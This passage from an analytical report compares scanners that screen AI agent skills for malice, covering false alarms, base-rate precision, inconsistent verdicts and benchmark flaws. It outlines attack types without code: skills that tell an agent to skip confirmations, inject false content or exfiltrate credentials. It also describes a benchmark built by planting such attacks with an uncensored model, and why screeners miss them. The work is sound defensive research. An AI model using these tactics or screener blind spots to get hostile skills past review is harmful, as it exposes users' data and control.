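- *The Devil Wears Markdown* (2026) used a much smaller model, Qwen3:8B, and skill-scanner flagged 40 of 60 benign skills, or 67%.

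A false-positive rate for "skill-scanner with a language model" therefore means little without the model and the dataset.

### What happens when stages are combined

Some of the differences in the table follow from simple probability. Suppose the static rules flag a share r₁ of malicious skills and a share f₁ of benign ones, and the model, working separately, flags r₂ and f₂. If either may block a skill, the skill gets through only when both let it pass:

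recall = 1 − (1 − r₁)(1 − r₂)

false-positive rate = 1 − (1 − f₁)(1 − f₂)

If the model must confirm whatever the rules flag, both have to agree before anything happens:

recall = r₁ × r₂

false-positive rate = f₁ × f₂

If two checks each have 90% recall and a 10% false-positive rate, and their errors are independent, blocking a skill when either check flags it raises recall to 99% and the false-positive rate to 19%. Requiring both checks to flag it lowers recall to 81% and the false-positive rate to 1%.

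The formulas assume that, among harmless skills and among malicious skills separately, a flag from the rules does not change the chance of a flag from the model. Real screeners violate this assumption because rules and models both tend to flag passwords and installers. Even so, adding a second stage that can only add blocks never lowers recall or the false-positive rate, and adding one that can only remove blocks never raises either.

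Cisco's skill-scanner blocks a skill if either its static rules or its model flags it. The rules alone blocked 71 of the 591 harmless skills, and adding a model raised this to between 98 and 105, depending on the model. Qwen3.6 caught 523 of the 566 malicious skills that the rules had missed, and wrongly flagged only 34 of the 520 harmless skills that they had passed (6.5%). About two thirds of the false alarms in this configuration therefore came from the rules. Because the model can't overturn a block by the rules, even a perfect model would leave the false-positive rate at 12.0%.

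If skill-scanner's rules and model flag skills independently, dropping the rules would let through about 24 more malicious skills and clear about 66 harmless ones. The 66 is probably too high, because a model will often flag the same harmless skills that a rule does.

The screener has an option that can go below the 12.0%, but Yang and colleagues did not switch it on. This "meta-analyzer" has a model review all findings, including those from the rules, and filter out likely false alarms, according to Cisco's *Frequently Asked Questions*. Another option runs the model several times and keeps the findings that most runs agree on. It affects only the model's own findings, so it cannot remove a false alarm that comes from a rule.

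SkillSpector both adds and removes. If its review could only discard what the rules had found, recall could not exceed 52.0%, yet it reached between 68.7% and 94.2%, because the model-based analysers contribute findings of their own before the review. As a rough formula, with h for the share of wrongly flagged skills that are still flagged after the review:

false-positive rate = h × [1 − (1 − f₁)(1 − f₂)]

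The static rules wrongly flag 17.3% of benign skills (f₁). If the analysers independently flagged 10% of benign skills, the two together would flag 25.6%, and the review would have to clear about a third of those to return to 17.3%. This calculation assumes that the review accepts or rejects a whole skill, whereas SkillSpector drops individual findings and then adds up the points.

In the review, Qwen3.6 and DeepSeek-V4 removed more false alarms than they added, lowering the false-positive rate to 7.0% and 10.3%, respectively. GPT-5.4 added more than it removed, raising the rate to 22.2%. The review also discards correct findings, and Qwen3.6, which had the lowest false-positive rate, also had the lowest recall.

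The same arithmetic applies to a hub that runs several screeners. Tencent summarises an analysis of OpenClaw's dataset of 67,453 ClawHub skills, which compared the hub's static rules, VirusTotal and SkillSpector. No two of them overlapped on more than 10.4% of the skills they flagged, and 81.9% of flagged skills were flagged by only one. A hub that blocked every skill flagged by any of the three would block nearly all of their false positives too. If it blocked only the skills that all three flagged, it would block 0.69% of the flagged skills.

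### What sets off a false alarm

Yang and colleagues read up to three of the findings behind each wrong block and sorted 2,790 findings by cause. The 1,445 wrong blocks in the table above involve only 591 benign skills, because a skill is counted once for each screener and model that blocked it.

| Cause | Share | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Access to credentials or local data | 36% | clawcall, which makes phone calls for the user, sends its API key to the service that issued it |
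| Code that looks exploitable | 19% | skillscan-security mistakes an ordinary JavaScript function declaration for code that runs text as a program |
| Mismatch with the declared scope | 12% | skill-scanner reports undeclared use of the Bash shell in a skill that declares it in a longer form |
| Instruction-like text | 10% | a skill tells the agent to start phase 3 of a task without asking the user |
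| Installers and remote code | 9% | SkillSpector flags the official installation command of SDKMAN, a developer tool, because someone could compromise the download |
| Content the screener could not inspect | 6% | skill-scanner treats incomplete coverage as a high-severity problem |
| Harmful-content judgments | 3% | SkillSpector with GPT-5.4 objects that vibetrader has no risk warnings for live trades |
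| Dependencies | 3% | SkillSpector ignores version limits when it looks up known flaws, and reports flaws that do not apply |
| Hidden content | under 1% | invisible spaces that conceal nothing |

In most of these cases, the screener correctly identified what the skill does. Of the credential findings, 47% concerned normal use of a service, such as logging in, and 39% concerned local files, such as the skill's own settings. Only 14% came from a placeholder, a description or a stray keyword. The code findings were less reliable. The screener misread the text in 45% of them, for example by taking an example in the documentation for a command that the skill runs. In another 54%, the operation was real but used only local inputs, such as the user's own files, which an outside attacker does not control.

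Roughly 29% of the findings in the four largest categories misdescribed what was in the skill, and better pattern matching could remove those. The rest describe something the skill does contain, and to dismiss them a screener has to work out what the operation is for and where the data goes. Guo and colleagues saw the same pattern on 4,000 benign skills in their benchmark, where model-based screeners flagged skills that had good reason to install helpers, run shell commands or request tokens.

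Each screener's false alarms also reflect what its designers asked it to look for. SkillSpector has a model call that compares a skill's declared scope with its actual behaviour, and 40% of the false alarms it raised with a model were about mismatches between the two. AI-Infra-Guard's audit stage looks for exploitable weaknesses as well as malice, and 52% of its false alarms were about code that looked exploitable. The red flags in skill-vetter include keys and credential files, and its largest group of false alarms, at 42%, was about access to credentials or local data.

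Whether all of these are mistakes depends on the screener's purpose. NVIDIA's *Scan Agent Skills Before Installation* says that SkillSpector looks for vulnerabilities and policy risks as well as malicious patterns, and it advises publishers to fix or formally accept every high or critical finding before release. It is reasonable to tell a publisher about a missing permission declaration. In 43% of the scope findings the mismatch was real, and in another 18% the skill did lack a declaration. The same score is a problem when a hub or user treats it as a judgment about malice. Yang and colleagues collected SkillSpector's audits of 84,560 skills on ClawHub. Of those skills, 50.4% had a finding rated high or above, and SkillSpector recommended against installing 45.8%.

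Scanners can flag a harmless skill for telling the agent to be careful, because a safety rule and an attack can use much the same words. *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* (2026) tested newer versions of skill-scanner and SkillSpector on directives that loosen a user's control over the agent, such as telling it to skip a confirmation. In every setup but one, between 23% and 29% of the flags fell on directives that tighten control instead. The exception was skill-scanner with GPT-5.4, at 13%.

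The wording of the question made a large difference here, as it did when Shi and colleagues asked a model about tool descriptions. GPT-5.4 reached an F1 of 0.65 when the researchers asked it directly whether a directive loosened control. The two screeners, whose prompts asked about malice, reached at most 0.36 with the same model available. Some of the model's apparent poor judgment may therefore result from a poorly chosen question. Revised instructions also reduced skill-vetter's false alarms in most of the settings that Yang and colleagues tried.

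Unreadable content is a harder case. Cisco's *Features* describes a score for how much of a skill's content, weighted by file size, the screener could analyse. By default, a skill that scores below 70% counts as high risk, and a low score is also recorded as a finding. Yang and colleagues object that a gap in the inspection is a reason for uncertainty, not evidence of malice. This is logically correct, but if a screener passes whatever it cannot read, attackers can hide their code in unreadable files. The ClawHavoc campaign hid malware in a password-protected archive. A separate label for skills that need human review would suit these cases better than blocking or passing them.

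### Scanning the same skill again

A screener with a language model can also change its mind about a skill that has not changed. Yang and colleagues ran the four model-based screeners three times with Qwen3.6 and counted the skills that did not get the same verdict every time:

| Screener | MalWild | MalSkillBench-Wild | Other five datasets |
|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 16.3% | 2.4% | 1.2–6.3% |
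| skill-vetter | 33.3% | 10.2% | 2.5–11.0% |
| SkillSpector | 57.4% | 42.2% | 11.7–39.2% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 64.3% | 31.9% | 11.2–24.4% |

AI-Infra-Guard's verdicts on MalWild were not much more consistent than three tosses of a fair coin, which give mixed results 75% of the time. Yang and colleagues had turned off Qwen3.6's reasoning for this screener after single audits took more than 1,000 seconds, so the verdicts may be more consistent with other settings.

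A screener's F1 can stay nearly the same from run to run even when many of its verdicts change. Over the three runs, SkillSpector gave inconsistent verdicts on 42.2% of the skills in MalSkillBench-Wild, yet the standard deviation of its F1 there was only 0.016. If 20 malicious skills go from blocked to passed and 20 other malicious skills go from passed to blocked, F1 stays the same. The standard deviation was 0.02 or less in 23 of the 28 combinations of screener and dataset. The clearest exception was AI-Infra-Guard on MalWild, at 0.061.

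Models produce text by sampling from probabilities, so some variation is expected. Setting the sampling temperature to zero makes the model always choose the most likely next token, but some variation remains because the hardware introduces small numerical differences when processing requests. Yang and colleagues cite Cisco's own measurements, in which 14% of skill-scanner's verdicts changed over five runs at temperature zero.

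The blocking rules probably make this worse. In AI-Infra-Guard, a skill can go from blocked to passed when one finding drops from high to medium severity, even though the model's reading of the file has hardly changed. Screeners that call the model many times also have more points where runs can diverge, which is consistent with the good result for skill-scanner, which uses a single prompt. MalWild is difficult for all the screeners because its benign skills looked malicious enough to fool the people who first labelled them.

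Repeating the scan and taking a majority vote reduces errors that the screener makes in fewer than half of its runs, but makes more frequent errors even more common. If a screener blocks a skill with probability p in each run, the majority of three independent runs blocks it with probability 3p² − 2p³. If a single run would block a harmless skill 20% of the time, voting lowers that to 10.4%. For a malicious skill, voting raises a 90% chance of a block to 97.2%, but lowers a 40% chance to 35.2%. It also triples the number of model calls.

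Hubs that scan each upload once face the opposite problem, because authors can try again. An honest publisher may change a line, upload the skill again and find it is no longer blocked, even though the change had nothing to do with it. An attacker can deliberately resubmit a skill until it passes. If the screener blocks a malicious skill 70% of the time and the hub allows three independent attempts, the skill has a 66% chance of getting through at least once.

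## What test scores say about a hub where malicious skills are rare

Malicious skills made up 60% of the test set that Yang and colleagues used, but 0.16% (157 of 98,380) of the skills on the two hubs that Liu and colleagues surveyed. Because of this difference, a screener can be right about 96% of the skills it flags in the test and wrong about 98% of those it flags on a hub, even if its recall and false-positive rate stay the same.

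### From recall and false alarms to precision

Take a hub with N skills, of which a share p (the prevalence) is malicious. A screener with recall r flags r × p × N malicious skills. If its false-positive rate is f, it also flags f × (1 − p) × N benign ones. N cancels out of the precision:

precision = r × p / (r × p + f × (1 − p))

In Yang and colleagues' test, skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 had a recall of 93.0% and a false-positive rate of 6.3%. At a prevalence of 0.16%, a hub of 100,000 skills contains 160 malicious ones. The screener would catch 149 of them and miss 11. It would also flag 6,290 of the 99,840 benign skills. Only 149 of its 6,439 alarms would be correct, so its precision would be 2.3%.

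| Screener | Prevalence | Correct alarms | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 | 0.16% | 149 | 6,290 | 2.3% |
| skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 | 8.8% | 8,184 | 5,746 | 59% |
| VirusTotal | 0.16% | 35 | 100 | 26% |

The 8.8% is the share of skills on OpenClaw's hub that Wu, Li and Liu's classifier labelled malicious, and it is probably much too high. The rates for VirusTotal come from MalSkillBench, Guo and colleagues' benchmark, where it caught 21.6% of the malicious skills and flagged 4 of 4,000 benign ones, giving a precision of 99.5%.

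A screener reaches 50% precision when the ratio of its recall to its false-positive rate, r/f, equals (1 − p)/p, where p is the prevalence of malicious skills. At a prevalence of 0.16%, the required ratio is 624. Skill-vetter's ratio is about 15, and VirusTotal's is 216. For half of the skills it flags to be malicious, a screener with 93% recall would need a false-positive rate of 0.15%, or about one benign skill in 670. For 90% to be malicious, it could flag only one benign skill in 6,000.

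Most tests are too small to measure false-positive rates this low. ClawHub-Mod flagged none of the 591 benign skills in Yang and colleagues' test, but a screener with a true false-positive rate of 0.5% would also have about a 5% chance of flagging none. At that rate, ClawHub-Mod's precision on the hub would be 2.3%, although it scored 100% in the test. VirusTotal's 4 false alarms in 4,000 are compatible with a true rate from about 0.03% to 0.26%, which would put its precision on the hub between 12% and 56%. Its measured rate may also be too low, because Guo and colleagues took their benign skills from ClawHub after they had passed the hub's own screening, which included VirusTotal.

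### Why operators choose strict thresholds

A hub that blocks skills automatically can reduce false alarms by acting only on the most severe findings. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026, a different group from the Yang and colleagues cited so far) tested this by running the static rules of Cisco's skill-scanner on 150 malicious and 1,500 benign skills and recording the result at each severity level. The last two columns below apply the measured rates to the hub with 160 malicious skills among 100,000.

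| Lowest severity that counts as a flag | Recall | False-positive rate | Malicious skills caught | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Informational | 82.0% | 86.5% | 131 | 86,300 |
| Low | 48.0% | 18.7% | 77 | 18,600 |
| Medium | 47.3% | 17.4% | 76 | 17,400 |
| High | 6.7% | 1.3% | 11 | 1,300 |
| Critical | 4.7% | 0.6% | 7 | 600 |

At the rules' loosest setting, a skill they flag is slightly less likely to be malicious than one picked at random. At the strictest setting, they catch only 7 of the 160 malicious skills.

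Lowering the threshold from high to medium would catch 65 more malicious skills and cause about 16,100 more false alarms, or roughly 250 for each additional catch. That is worthwhile only if a missed malicious skill does more harm than 250 wrongly blocked skills. This is doubtful for a rarely installed skill, but could easily be true for one that steals passwords from the thousands of people who install it. However, false alarms bring immediate complaints and appeals from honest publishers, while nobody may notice a missed skill for months. This gives operators a strong reason to prefer high thresholds for automatic blocking.

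Skill-vetter, a better screener, fares much better in the same comparison. Replacing VirusTotal with it would catch 114 more malicious skills and add about 6,190 false alarms, or 54 for each additional catch.

### What the flag rates on ClawHub imply

At the other extreme, SkillSpector advised against installing 45.8% of the 84,560 ClawHub skills with usable results, or about 38,700 skills. At a prevalence of 0.16%, about 135 of the 84,560 would be malicious, so even if SkillSpector caught them all, only 0.35% of its warnings would be for malicious skills. At a prevalence of 8.8%, that share would be at most 19%.

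When malicious skills are rare, the share of all skills that a screener flags is close to its false-positive rate, so an operator can estimate that rate without labelling any skills. SkillSpector's false-positive rate on the hub must be at least 41%, even if 8.8% of the hub's skills are malicious and it flags all of them. In Yang and colleagues' test, the rate was between 7.0% and 22.2%, depending on the model.

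AI-Infra-Guard shows a similar gap. It reported at least one finding of high severity or above for 28.0% of 83,473 ClawHub skills. In the test, one such finding was enough to block a skill, and the false-positive rate under that rule was between 7.3% and 13.6%. SkillSpector reported at least one finding of low severity or above for 91.4% of skills, and AI-Infra-Guard did so for 55.2%.

The hub may run these screeners with different models or settings. Another likely reason is that a real hub also contains the risky and suspicious skills that the test left out.

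Test scores can also be too pessimistic. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Instructions to Exploits*, built a screener called SCS, which translates a skill's instructions into program-like steps and traces how data moves between those steps and the scripts. On 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, its precision averaged 80.2% across five language models. On 66,157 skills collected from ClawHub in April 2026, it flagged 2,473. The researchers confirmed 627 of these as malicious, a precision of 25%, after running them in a controlled environment and reviewing them by hand.

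Precision fell from 80% in the test to 25% on the hub, a smaller drop than the formula predicts. In the test, SCS had a recall of 95.2% and a false-positive rate of about 24%. Those rates would give a precision below 4% on the hub, but SCS flagged only about 2.8% of the hub skills that were not confirmed as malicious. Benign skills in the test were evidently harder to classify than typical ones on the hub, perhaps because many came from collections compiled for security research or from ClawHub's most-installed skills. The formula still holds, but an operator needs a false-positive rate measured on the hub itself. Recall is harder to measure on the hub, because Zhao and colleagues reviewed only the flagged skills and cannot tell how many malicious ones SCS missed.

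Prevalence also changes as a hub removes malicious skills. Two publishers had uploaded 552 of the 627 confirmed malicious skills, and ClawHub had removed all 552 by mid-July. Only 23 of the 627 were still identifiable in the registry. If those 23 were the only malicious skills left, skill-vetter's precision on this hub would be about 0.5%. The more thoroughly a hub removes malicious skills, the larger the share of skills flagged in the next scan that are false alarms. But during an attack, prevalence can be far higher among new uploads than in the hub as a whole.

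### A benchmark of attacks that ran in a sandbox

The calculation also needs a recall figure, which depends on the attacks in the benchmark. Guo and colleagues built MalSkillBench because the malicious skills found on hubs are too similar to one another to test a screener properly. Its 4,000 benign skills are the most downloaded on ClawHub. Of its 3,944 malicious skills, the researchers collected 703 from hubs, took 27 from the test suites of existing screeners and generated the other 3,214.

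They first defined 108 combinations of attack route, harmful behaviour and hiding place. For each combination, a language model with its refusals removed received examples of real attacks, either code from malicious Python packages or known prompt-injection texts. It worked an attack into a copy of a legitimate skill. The skill then had to pass a test:

1. A coding agent received an ordinary request that matched the skill's advertised purpose and ran the skill in an isolated container for up to six minutes.
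2. Monitoring tools recorded network connections, file access and the programs that started.
3. The skill passed if this record or the agent's output matched an expected sign of the attack, such as a connection to a particular server. It also passed if GPT-5.4-mini concluded with at least 70% confidence that the intended behaviour had occurred.
4. A failed skill went back to the first model for revision, up to three times.

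3,214 of 3,757 candidates passed. The pass rate was 94.5% for attacks in code, 91.9% for attacks split between code and instructions, and 75.8% for attacks in the instructions alone. The evidence is weakest for the last group, because a manipulated answer does not appear in the system records. A skill in this group also passed if the agent noticed the attack and refused to follow it, so some of these skills may never have worked. But two researchers reviewed 300 of the generated skills, 100 from each group, and agreed with every label.

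Guo and colleagues ran nine screeners on the benchmark in twelve configurations. These are five of them:

| Screener | Judge | Precision | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentry's skill scanner | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 80.5% | 98.4% | 23.4% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | GPT-5.4-mini | 84.6% | 86.6% | 15.5% |
| Cisco's skill-scanner | GPT-5.4-mini | 71.4% | 92.7% | 36.6% |
| Snyk Agent Scan | none | 93.2% | 28.7% | 2.1% |
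| VirusTotal | none | 99.5% | 21.6% | 0.1% |

Sentry's scanner has the best F1 of the twelve, 88.6%, while VirusTotal ranks ninth with 35.5%. On a hub where 0.16% of skills are malicious, however, VirusTotal would have the higher precision, 26% against 0.7%. Sentry's scanner would catch 157 of the 160 malicious skills but raise about 23,400 false alarms. F1 on a balanced benchmark is therefore a poor guide for choosing a screener to block skills automatically.

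The paper's abstract misstates the result for Sentry's scanner. According to the abstract, the strongest screener reaches 98.4% recall on code attacks and collapses on attacks in the instructions. The results in the body of the paper give 98.4% as the recall on the whole benchmark. By attack route, the figures are:

| Screener | Code | Code and instructions | Instructions alone |
|---|---|---|---|
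| Sentry's scanner with Claude Haiku 4.5 | 99.8% | 99.8% | 97.6% |
| AI-Infra-Guard with GPT-5.4-mini | 99.2% | 99.1% | 74.8% |
| skill-scanner with GPT-5.4-mini | 96.5% | 98.9% | 83.1% |
| skill-scanner, static rules alone | 46.9% | 72.0% | 18.7% |

These rates appear to cover only the generated skills, because the numbers of missed skills match the totals only if they do. Sentry's scanner wrongly flags 937 benign skills, but its recall does not collapse on instruction attacks. The other screeners lose recall on these attacks, most of all when a skill tells the agent to slip biased or false content into its answers. AI-Infra-Guard caught 35.8% of those skills, and skill-scanner with GPT-5.4-mini caught 32.1%.

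### Why VirusTotal's recall rises by 66 points

VirusTotal's recall was 87.9% on the 703 skills collected from hubs, compared with 21.6% on the full benchmark. Snyk Agent Scan's recall was also higher on the collected skills (77.2%, compared with 28.7%), while AI-Infra-Guard's was lower (74.0%, compared with 86.6%). Anyone who tested only on the collected skills would rank VirusTotal among the best screeners.

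A screener's overall recall is the average of its recall on each type of attack, weighted by how common each type is. Of the 703 collected skills, 609 deliver malware, mostly through a fake prerequisite. VirusTotal caught 99.3% of those 609, which accounts for 86 points of its 87.9% overall recall. It caught only 9.1% of the 33 skills that steal credentials and 16.7% of the 18 that send out other data. The collected skills came from public reports of attacks, so antivirus companies had probably already seen much of the malware.

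Which recall to use depends on the attacks a hub will face. If the next attack resembles the campaigns of early 2026, 87.9% is the better forecast, and VirusTotal's precision at a prevalence of 0.16% would be 58% instead of 26%. If attackers switch to plain instructions, 21.6% may be too high. The researchers chose the weight of each attack type in the full benchmark without basing it on how often attackers use that type, so the benchmark's recall is not a forecast. An operator would do better to weight the recall for each attack type by how common that type is in recent uploads.

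ClawHub-Mod's recall of 7.4% in Yang and colleagues' test has a similar explanation. It caught 41.2% of the malicious skills from Guo and colleagues' collection, and at most 2% in each of the other six datasets. The hub's rules therefore catch a good part of the attacks the hub has suffered, but almost no others.

### Copies and disputed labels

The 703 collected skills include far fewer than 703 independent examples. Two accounts published 569 of the skills, and only 193 distinct skills remained when Yang and colleagues compared the files in each one, ignoring information added by the hub. A screener that catches one copy will almost certainly catch the others, so a single correct decision or a single mistake can count dozens of times.

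Copies matter even more if a screener has learned from examples, because the same skill can end up in both the training and the test data. *Malicious SkillBench* (Wang, Liu and colleagues, 2026) combined public collections of malicious skills and found many such overlaps. (One of its sources is the similarly named MalSkillBench, by Guo and colleagues.) The 11 sources contained 8,414 malicious skills, and 7,539 remained after removing copies, including those that differed only in formatting. Many of these were variations on a shared template, and a similarity measure sorted them into 4,588 groups.

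Labels are another source of error. Wang and colleagues found 34 skills that one source had labelled malicious and another benign, and left them out. Yang and colleagues went further and reread every skill that its compilers had found on a hub:

| Collection | Distinct skills | Malicious | Benign | Risky or suspicious |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues | 157 | 95 | 34 | 28 |
| Guo and colleagues | 193 | 148 | 19 | 26 |

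The original compilers had labelled all 350 skills as malicious, and in both projects two researchers had reviewed each one. Much of the disagreement is probably about definitions, since Yang and colleagues required evidence of intent to harm the user. The disagreement still affects the scores. A screener that passed all 34 skills relabelled benign in Liu and colleagues' collection would have 34 misses under the old labels and 34 correct decisions under the new ones.

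The disagreement also affects the prevalence. If 95 of the 98,380 skills are malicious, prevalence falls from 0.16% to 0.10%, and skill-vetter's precision on a hub falls from 2.3% to 1.4%.

### Sources a screener has not seen before

Wang and colleagues also tested how well a screener copes with skills from an unfamiliar source. Their final set has 7,505 malicious and 2,235 benign skills. They trained simple classifiers, which use word frequencies and no language model, on the instruction text of part of the set. They then tested them on the rest, dividing the data in three ways. The score is macro-F1, the average of the F1 for malicious skills and the F1 for benign ones. For the strongest classifier it was:

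- 0.932 when they divided the skills at random.
- 0.916 when they kept all malicious skills that shared a template on the same side of the division.
- 0.665 when they held back three entire sources for the test.

Shared templates thus explain little of the drop. In the test on the three unseen sources, the classifier still caught 802 of 839 malicious skills (95.6%), but it flagged 340 of 545 benign ones (62.4%), compared with 9.4% under the random division. Most of the 340 came from a single source with its own conventions. The classifier had apparently learned what benign skills looked like in its training sources and treated anything else as malicious. Six of the 11 sources contribute no benign skills, which makes this shortcut easy to learn. Balancing the training data reduced the false-positive rate on unseen sources to 43.3%.

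A language model used as a judge has not trained on these labels, so it cannot take quite the same shortcut, but its scores also fail to carry over to new data. Yang and colleagues ran skill-vetter on an eighth dataset, SkillSafetyBench, outside their main test. With Qwen3.6, skill-vetter missed about 109 of the 154 malicious skills, and its recall was 29%, compared with 93.0% in the main test. Recall was about 33% with DeepSeek-V4 and 66% with GPT-5.4. Skill-vetter erred in the opposite direction from the word-frequency classifier, flagging only 2 of the 112 benign skills on average with Qwen3.6. On a hub full of attacks like these, it would be much less useful than its main results suggest.

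### One screener in six studies

Cisco's skill-scanner appears in more of these studies than any other screener. Its recall ranges from 2.5% to 98.3%:

| Study | Malicious / benign skills | Mode | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Wang and colleagues, unseen sources | 839 / 545 | rules, high severity or above | 2.5% | 1.1% |
| Yang, Fu and colleagues | 150 / 1,500 | rules, high severity or above | 6.7% | 1.3% |
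| Yang, Fu and colleagues | 150 / 1,500 | GPT-5.4-mini, critical only | 18.0% | 0.7% |
| Guo and colleagues | 3,944 / 4,000 | rules | 35.6% | 9.6% |
| Yang and colleagues | 886 / 591 | rules, high severity or above | 36.1% | 12.0% |
| Yang, Fu and colleagues | 150 / 1,500 | rules, any finding | 82.0% | 86.5% |
| *The Devil Wears Markdown* | 80 / 60 | Qwen3:8B | 85% | 67% |
| Yang and colleagues | 886 / 591 | GPT-5.4 | 88.1% | 16.6% |
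| *The Devil Wears Markdown* | 80 / 60 | rules, any finding | 91% | 55% |
| Guo and colleagues | 3,944 / 4,000 | GPT-5.4-mini | 92.7% | 36.6% |
| Yang and colleagues | 886 / 591 | Qwen3.6 | 95.1% | 17.8% |
| Guo and colleagues, collected skills only | 703 / 0 | GPT-5.4-mini | 98.2% | not measurable |
| Zhao and colleagues | 117 / 117 | GPT-5.4 | 98.3% | 57% |

The table leaves out precision because it depends on the share of malicious skills, which varies greatly between the studies. In Yang, Fu and colleagues' test, where 9% of the skills are malicious, the rules have a recall of 47.3% and a false-positive rate of 17.4%, which gives a precision of 21%. The same two rates would give a precision of 73% in a test with equal numbers of malicious and benign skills.

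Much of the range in recall comes from the threshold and whether a language model was used, but the input also matters. Wang and colleagues gave the scanner only each skill's main instruction text, without its scripts, so the rules for code had little to match and the 2.5% reflects only part of the tool.

The same may be true of the 6.7% recall. Yang, Fu and colleagues appear to have used the same dataset of 1,650 skills as Yang and colleagues, and both groups ran version 2.0.11 of the scanner. At the same minimum severity, the rules caught 6.7% of the 150 malicious skills in Yang, Fu and colleagues' study and 64.7% in Yang and colleagues' study. Yang and colleagues had restored each skill's scripts from the dataset before scanning. If Yang, Fu and colleagues scanned only the instruction files, that would explain both their lower recall and their lower false-positive rate.

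The effect of the model is easier to isolate on a shared set of skills. Yang and colleagues took 150 of their benign skills from the 4,000 in MalSkillBench. The rules alone wrongly flagged about 11% of those 150, close to the 9.6% that Guo and colleagues measured on all 4,000. With a language model, the false-positive rate was about 12% with GPT-5.4 in one study and 36.6% with GPT-5.4-mini in the other. The smaller model is the most likely cause of the difference, although the two groups may also have used different versions or settings. But a larger model doesn't guarantee few false alarms. In Zhao and colleagues' test, skill-scanner wrongly flagged 57% of the benign skills with GPT-5.4, and at least 39% with each of the five models they tried.

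The differences between these rows matter less than they seem to for a hub where 0.16% of skills are malicious. At that prevalence, precision would be between 0.15% and 3.8% for every row with a false-positive rate, and the configuration with the highest precision misses 82% of the malicious skills.

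## Why a screener that is right when it flags can miss many malicious skills

The simplest way to screen a skill with a language model is to show the model the whole package and ask whether it is malicious. Wu, Li and Liu tested this as a baseline for BIV, their method of comparing what a skill declares with what it does. They called Claude Opus 4.6 once for each of 906 skills, 404 of which were malicious. Opus flagged 281 skills and was right about 278 of them, a precision of 98.9%. But it missed the other 126 malicious skills, so its recall was 68.8%.

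The skills came from three sources. Two, Skill-Inject and SkillJect, are published methods for planting attacks in legitimate skills, and Wu, Li and Liu used both to generate new examples.

| Source | Malicious skills caught | Benign skills flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Real malware and benign skills from hubs | 14 of 44 (32%) | 2 of 410 |
| Skill-Inject | 138 of 160 (86%) | 1 of 42 |
| SkillJect | 126 of 200 (63%) | 0 of 50 |

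Opus did worst on the real malware. Its precision was also lower there, with 14 of 16 alarms correct (87.5%), so its overall precision of 98.9% depends heavily on the artificial attacks.

The sample of real malware is small. It comes from 157 malicious skills that Liu and colleagues had confirmed, but the public list gives only web addresses, and most of the repositories had disappeared. Wu, Li and Liu could retrieve 56 skills and dropped 12 in which they found no malicious behaviour. With the remaining 44, the 95% confidence interval for recall runs from 20% to 47%.

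In *SkillSieve*, Hou, Pang and colleagues (2026) found the same pattern with another model, Moonshot AI's Kimi 2.5. Their first test set had 400 ClawHub skills, 89 of which they had labelled malicious. A static filter cleared most of the 400, and Kimi judged the remaining 151 or so with a single prompt. It flagged 53 skills, all labelled malicious, for a precision of 100% and a recall of 59.6%.

But some of Kimi's 36 apparent misses may have been correct decisions, so its true recall could be well above 59.6%. After further human review, the test set in a later version of the paper has only 56 malicious skills among 390. Ten skills had disappeared from the hub in the meantime, so at least 23 of the original 89 malicious labels must have changed.

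When recall is low, a pass is only weak evidence that a skill is safe. On a hub where 0.16% of skills are malicious, a skill that the Opus baseline passes still has a 0.11% chance of being malicious, assuming the baseline's recall is 32%, as measured on real malware.

### Screeners that err the other way

Other language-model screeners catch nearly all malicious skills but raise many false alarms. Sentry's scanner, for example, caught 98.4% of the malicious skills in MalSkillBench and flagged 23.4% of the benign ones. How often a screener misses attacks therefore depends on its setup and threshold.

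Yang and colleagues tested four screeners on skills from the same collection that supplied the 44 pieces of real malware. After relabelling, they had 95 malicious and 34 benign skills. This is the recall of each screener with each model:

| Screener | Qwen3.6 | DeepSeek-V4 | GPT-5.4 |
|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 91.6% | 92.6% | 38.9% |
| SkillSpector | 48.4% | 77.9% | 98.9% |
| skill-vetter | 87.4% | 90.5% | 66.3% |
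| AI-Infra-Guard | 72.6% | 9.5% | 47.4% |

GPT-5.4 has the highest recall of the three models in SkillSpector and the lowest in skill-scanner and skill-vetter. The model and the skills were the same in each case, so they cannot explain this on their own. The screeners prompt the model with different questions and handle its answers differently.

A screener can also miss many attacks and be imprecise. With DeepSeek-V4, AI-Infra-Guard caught 9 of the 95 malicious skills, and its scores imply that it also flagged 9 of the 34 benign ones. Those 34 are unusually hard to classify.

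### Attacks that a screener finds and then lets through

Yang and colleagues read the reports and logs for each missed skill to see where the screener had failed. They counted an attack as identified only if a finding described the malicious behaviour itself. A skill counts once for each model that missed it, and the table leaves out 46 cases where the skill appeared to be mislabelled as malicious.

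| Screener | Misses | Attack not identified | Graded too low | Dismissed or filtered out | Share identified |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| skill-scanner | 185 | 66 | 119 | – | 64.3% |
| SkillSpector | 446 | 134 | 203 | 109 | 70.0% |
| skill-vetter | 167 | 16 | – | 151 | 90.4% |
| AI-Infra-Guard | 399 | 47 | 28 | 324 | 88.2% |

In most cases, then, the screener found the attack but did not block the skill. Screeners that use only static rules, by contrast, failed to identify the attack in 84% of their misses, either because no rule covered it or because the skill's author had written it as ordinary prose.

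SkillSpector's 70.0% is probably somewhat too high. The 109 filtered cases are skills that its static rules alone would have blocked but that passed after a model reviewed the findings. Yang and colleagues sorted these cases by verdict, without checking whether the discarded finding described the attack.

A finding is graded too low when it describes the attack but its severity is below the blocking threshold. For example, the static screener skillscan-security detected a skill uploading customer data, but reported this as undeclared network access and rated it medium, which was not enough to block the skill. Raising the severity would have caught this skill. But a hub that blocked every skill matching the same rule would stop 48.3% of malicious skills and also reject 29.3% of benign ones.

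When a model-based screener did not identify the attack, the model had often not received the relevant text or had been told not to report that kind of attack. In 39 of skill-scanner's 66 cases, the instructions never reached the model because they were too long. SkillSpector instructs its model-based analysers not to report the kinds of pattern that its static rules are meant to cover, so neither stage reports the attack if the rules fail to match it.

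### The reasons for dismissing an attack

Skill-vetter and AI-Infra-Guard dismissed an identified attack 475 times between them. Yang and colleagues sorted the dismissals by the reason in the screener's report:

| Reason | skill-vetter | AI-Infra-Guard |
|---|---|---|
| No executable code in the package | 92 | 90 |
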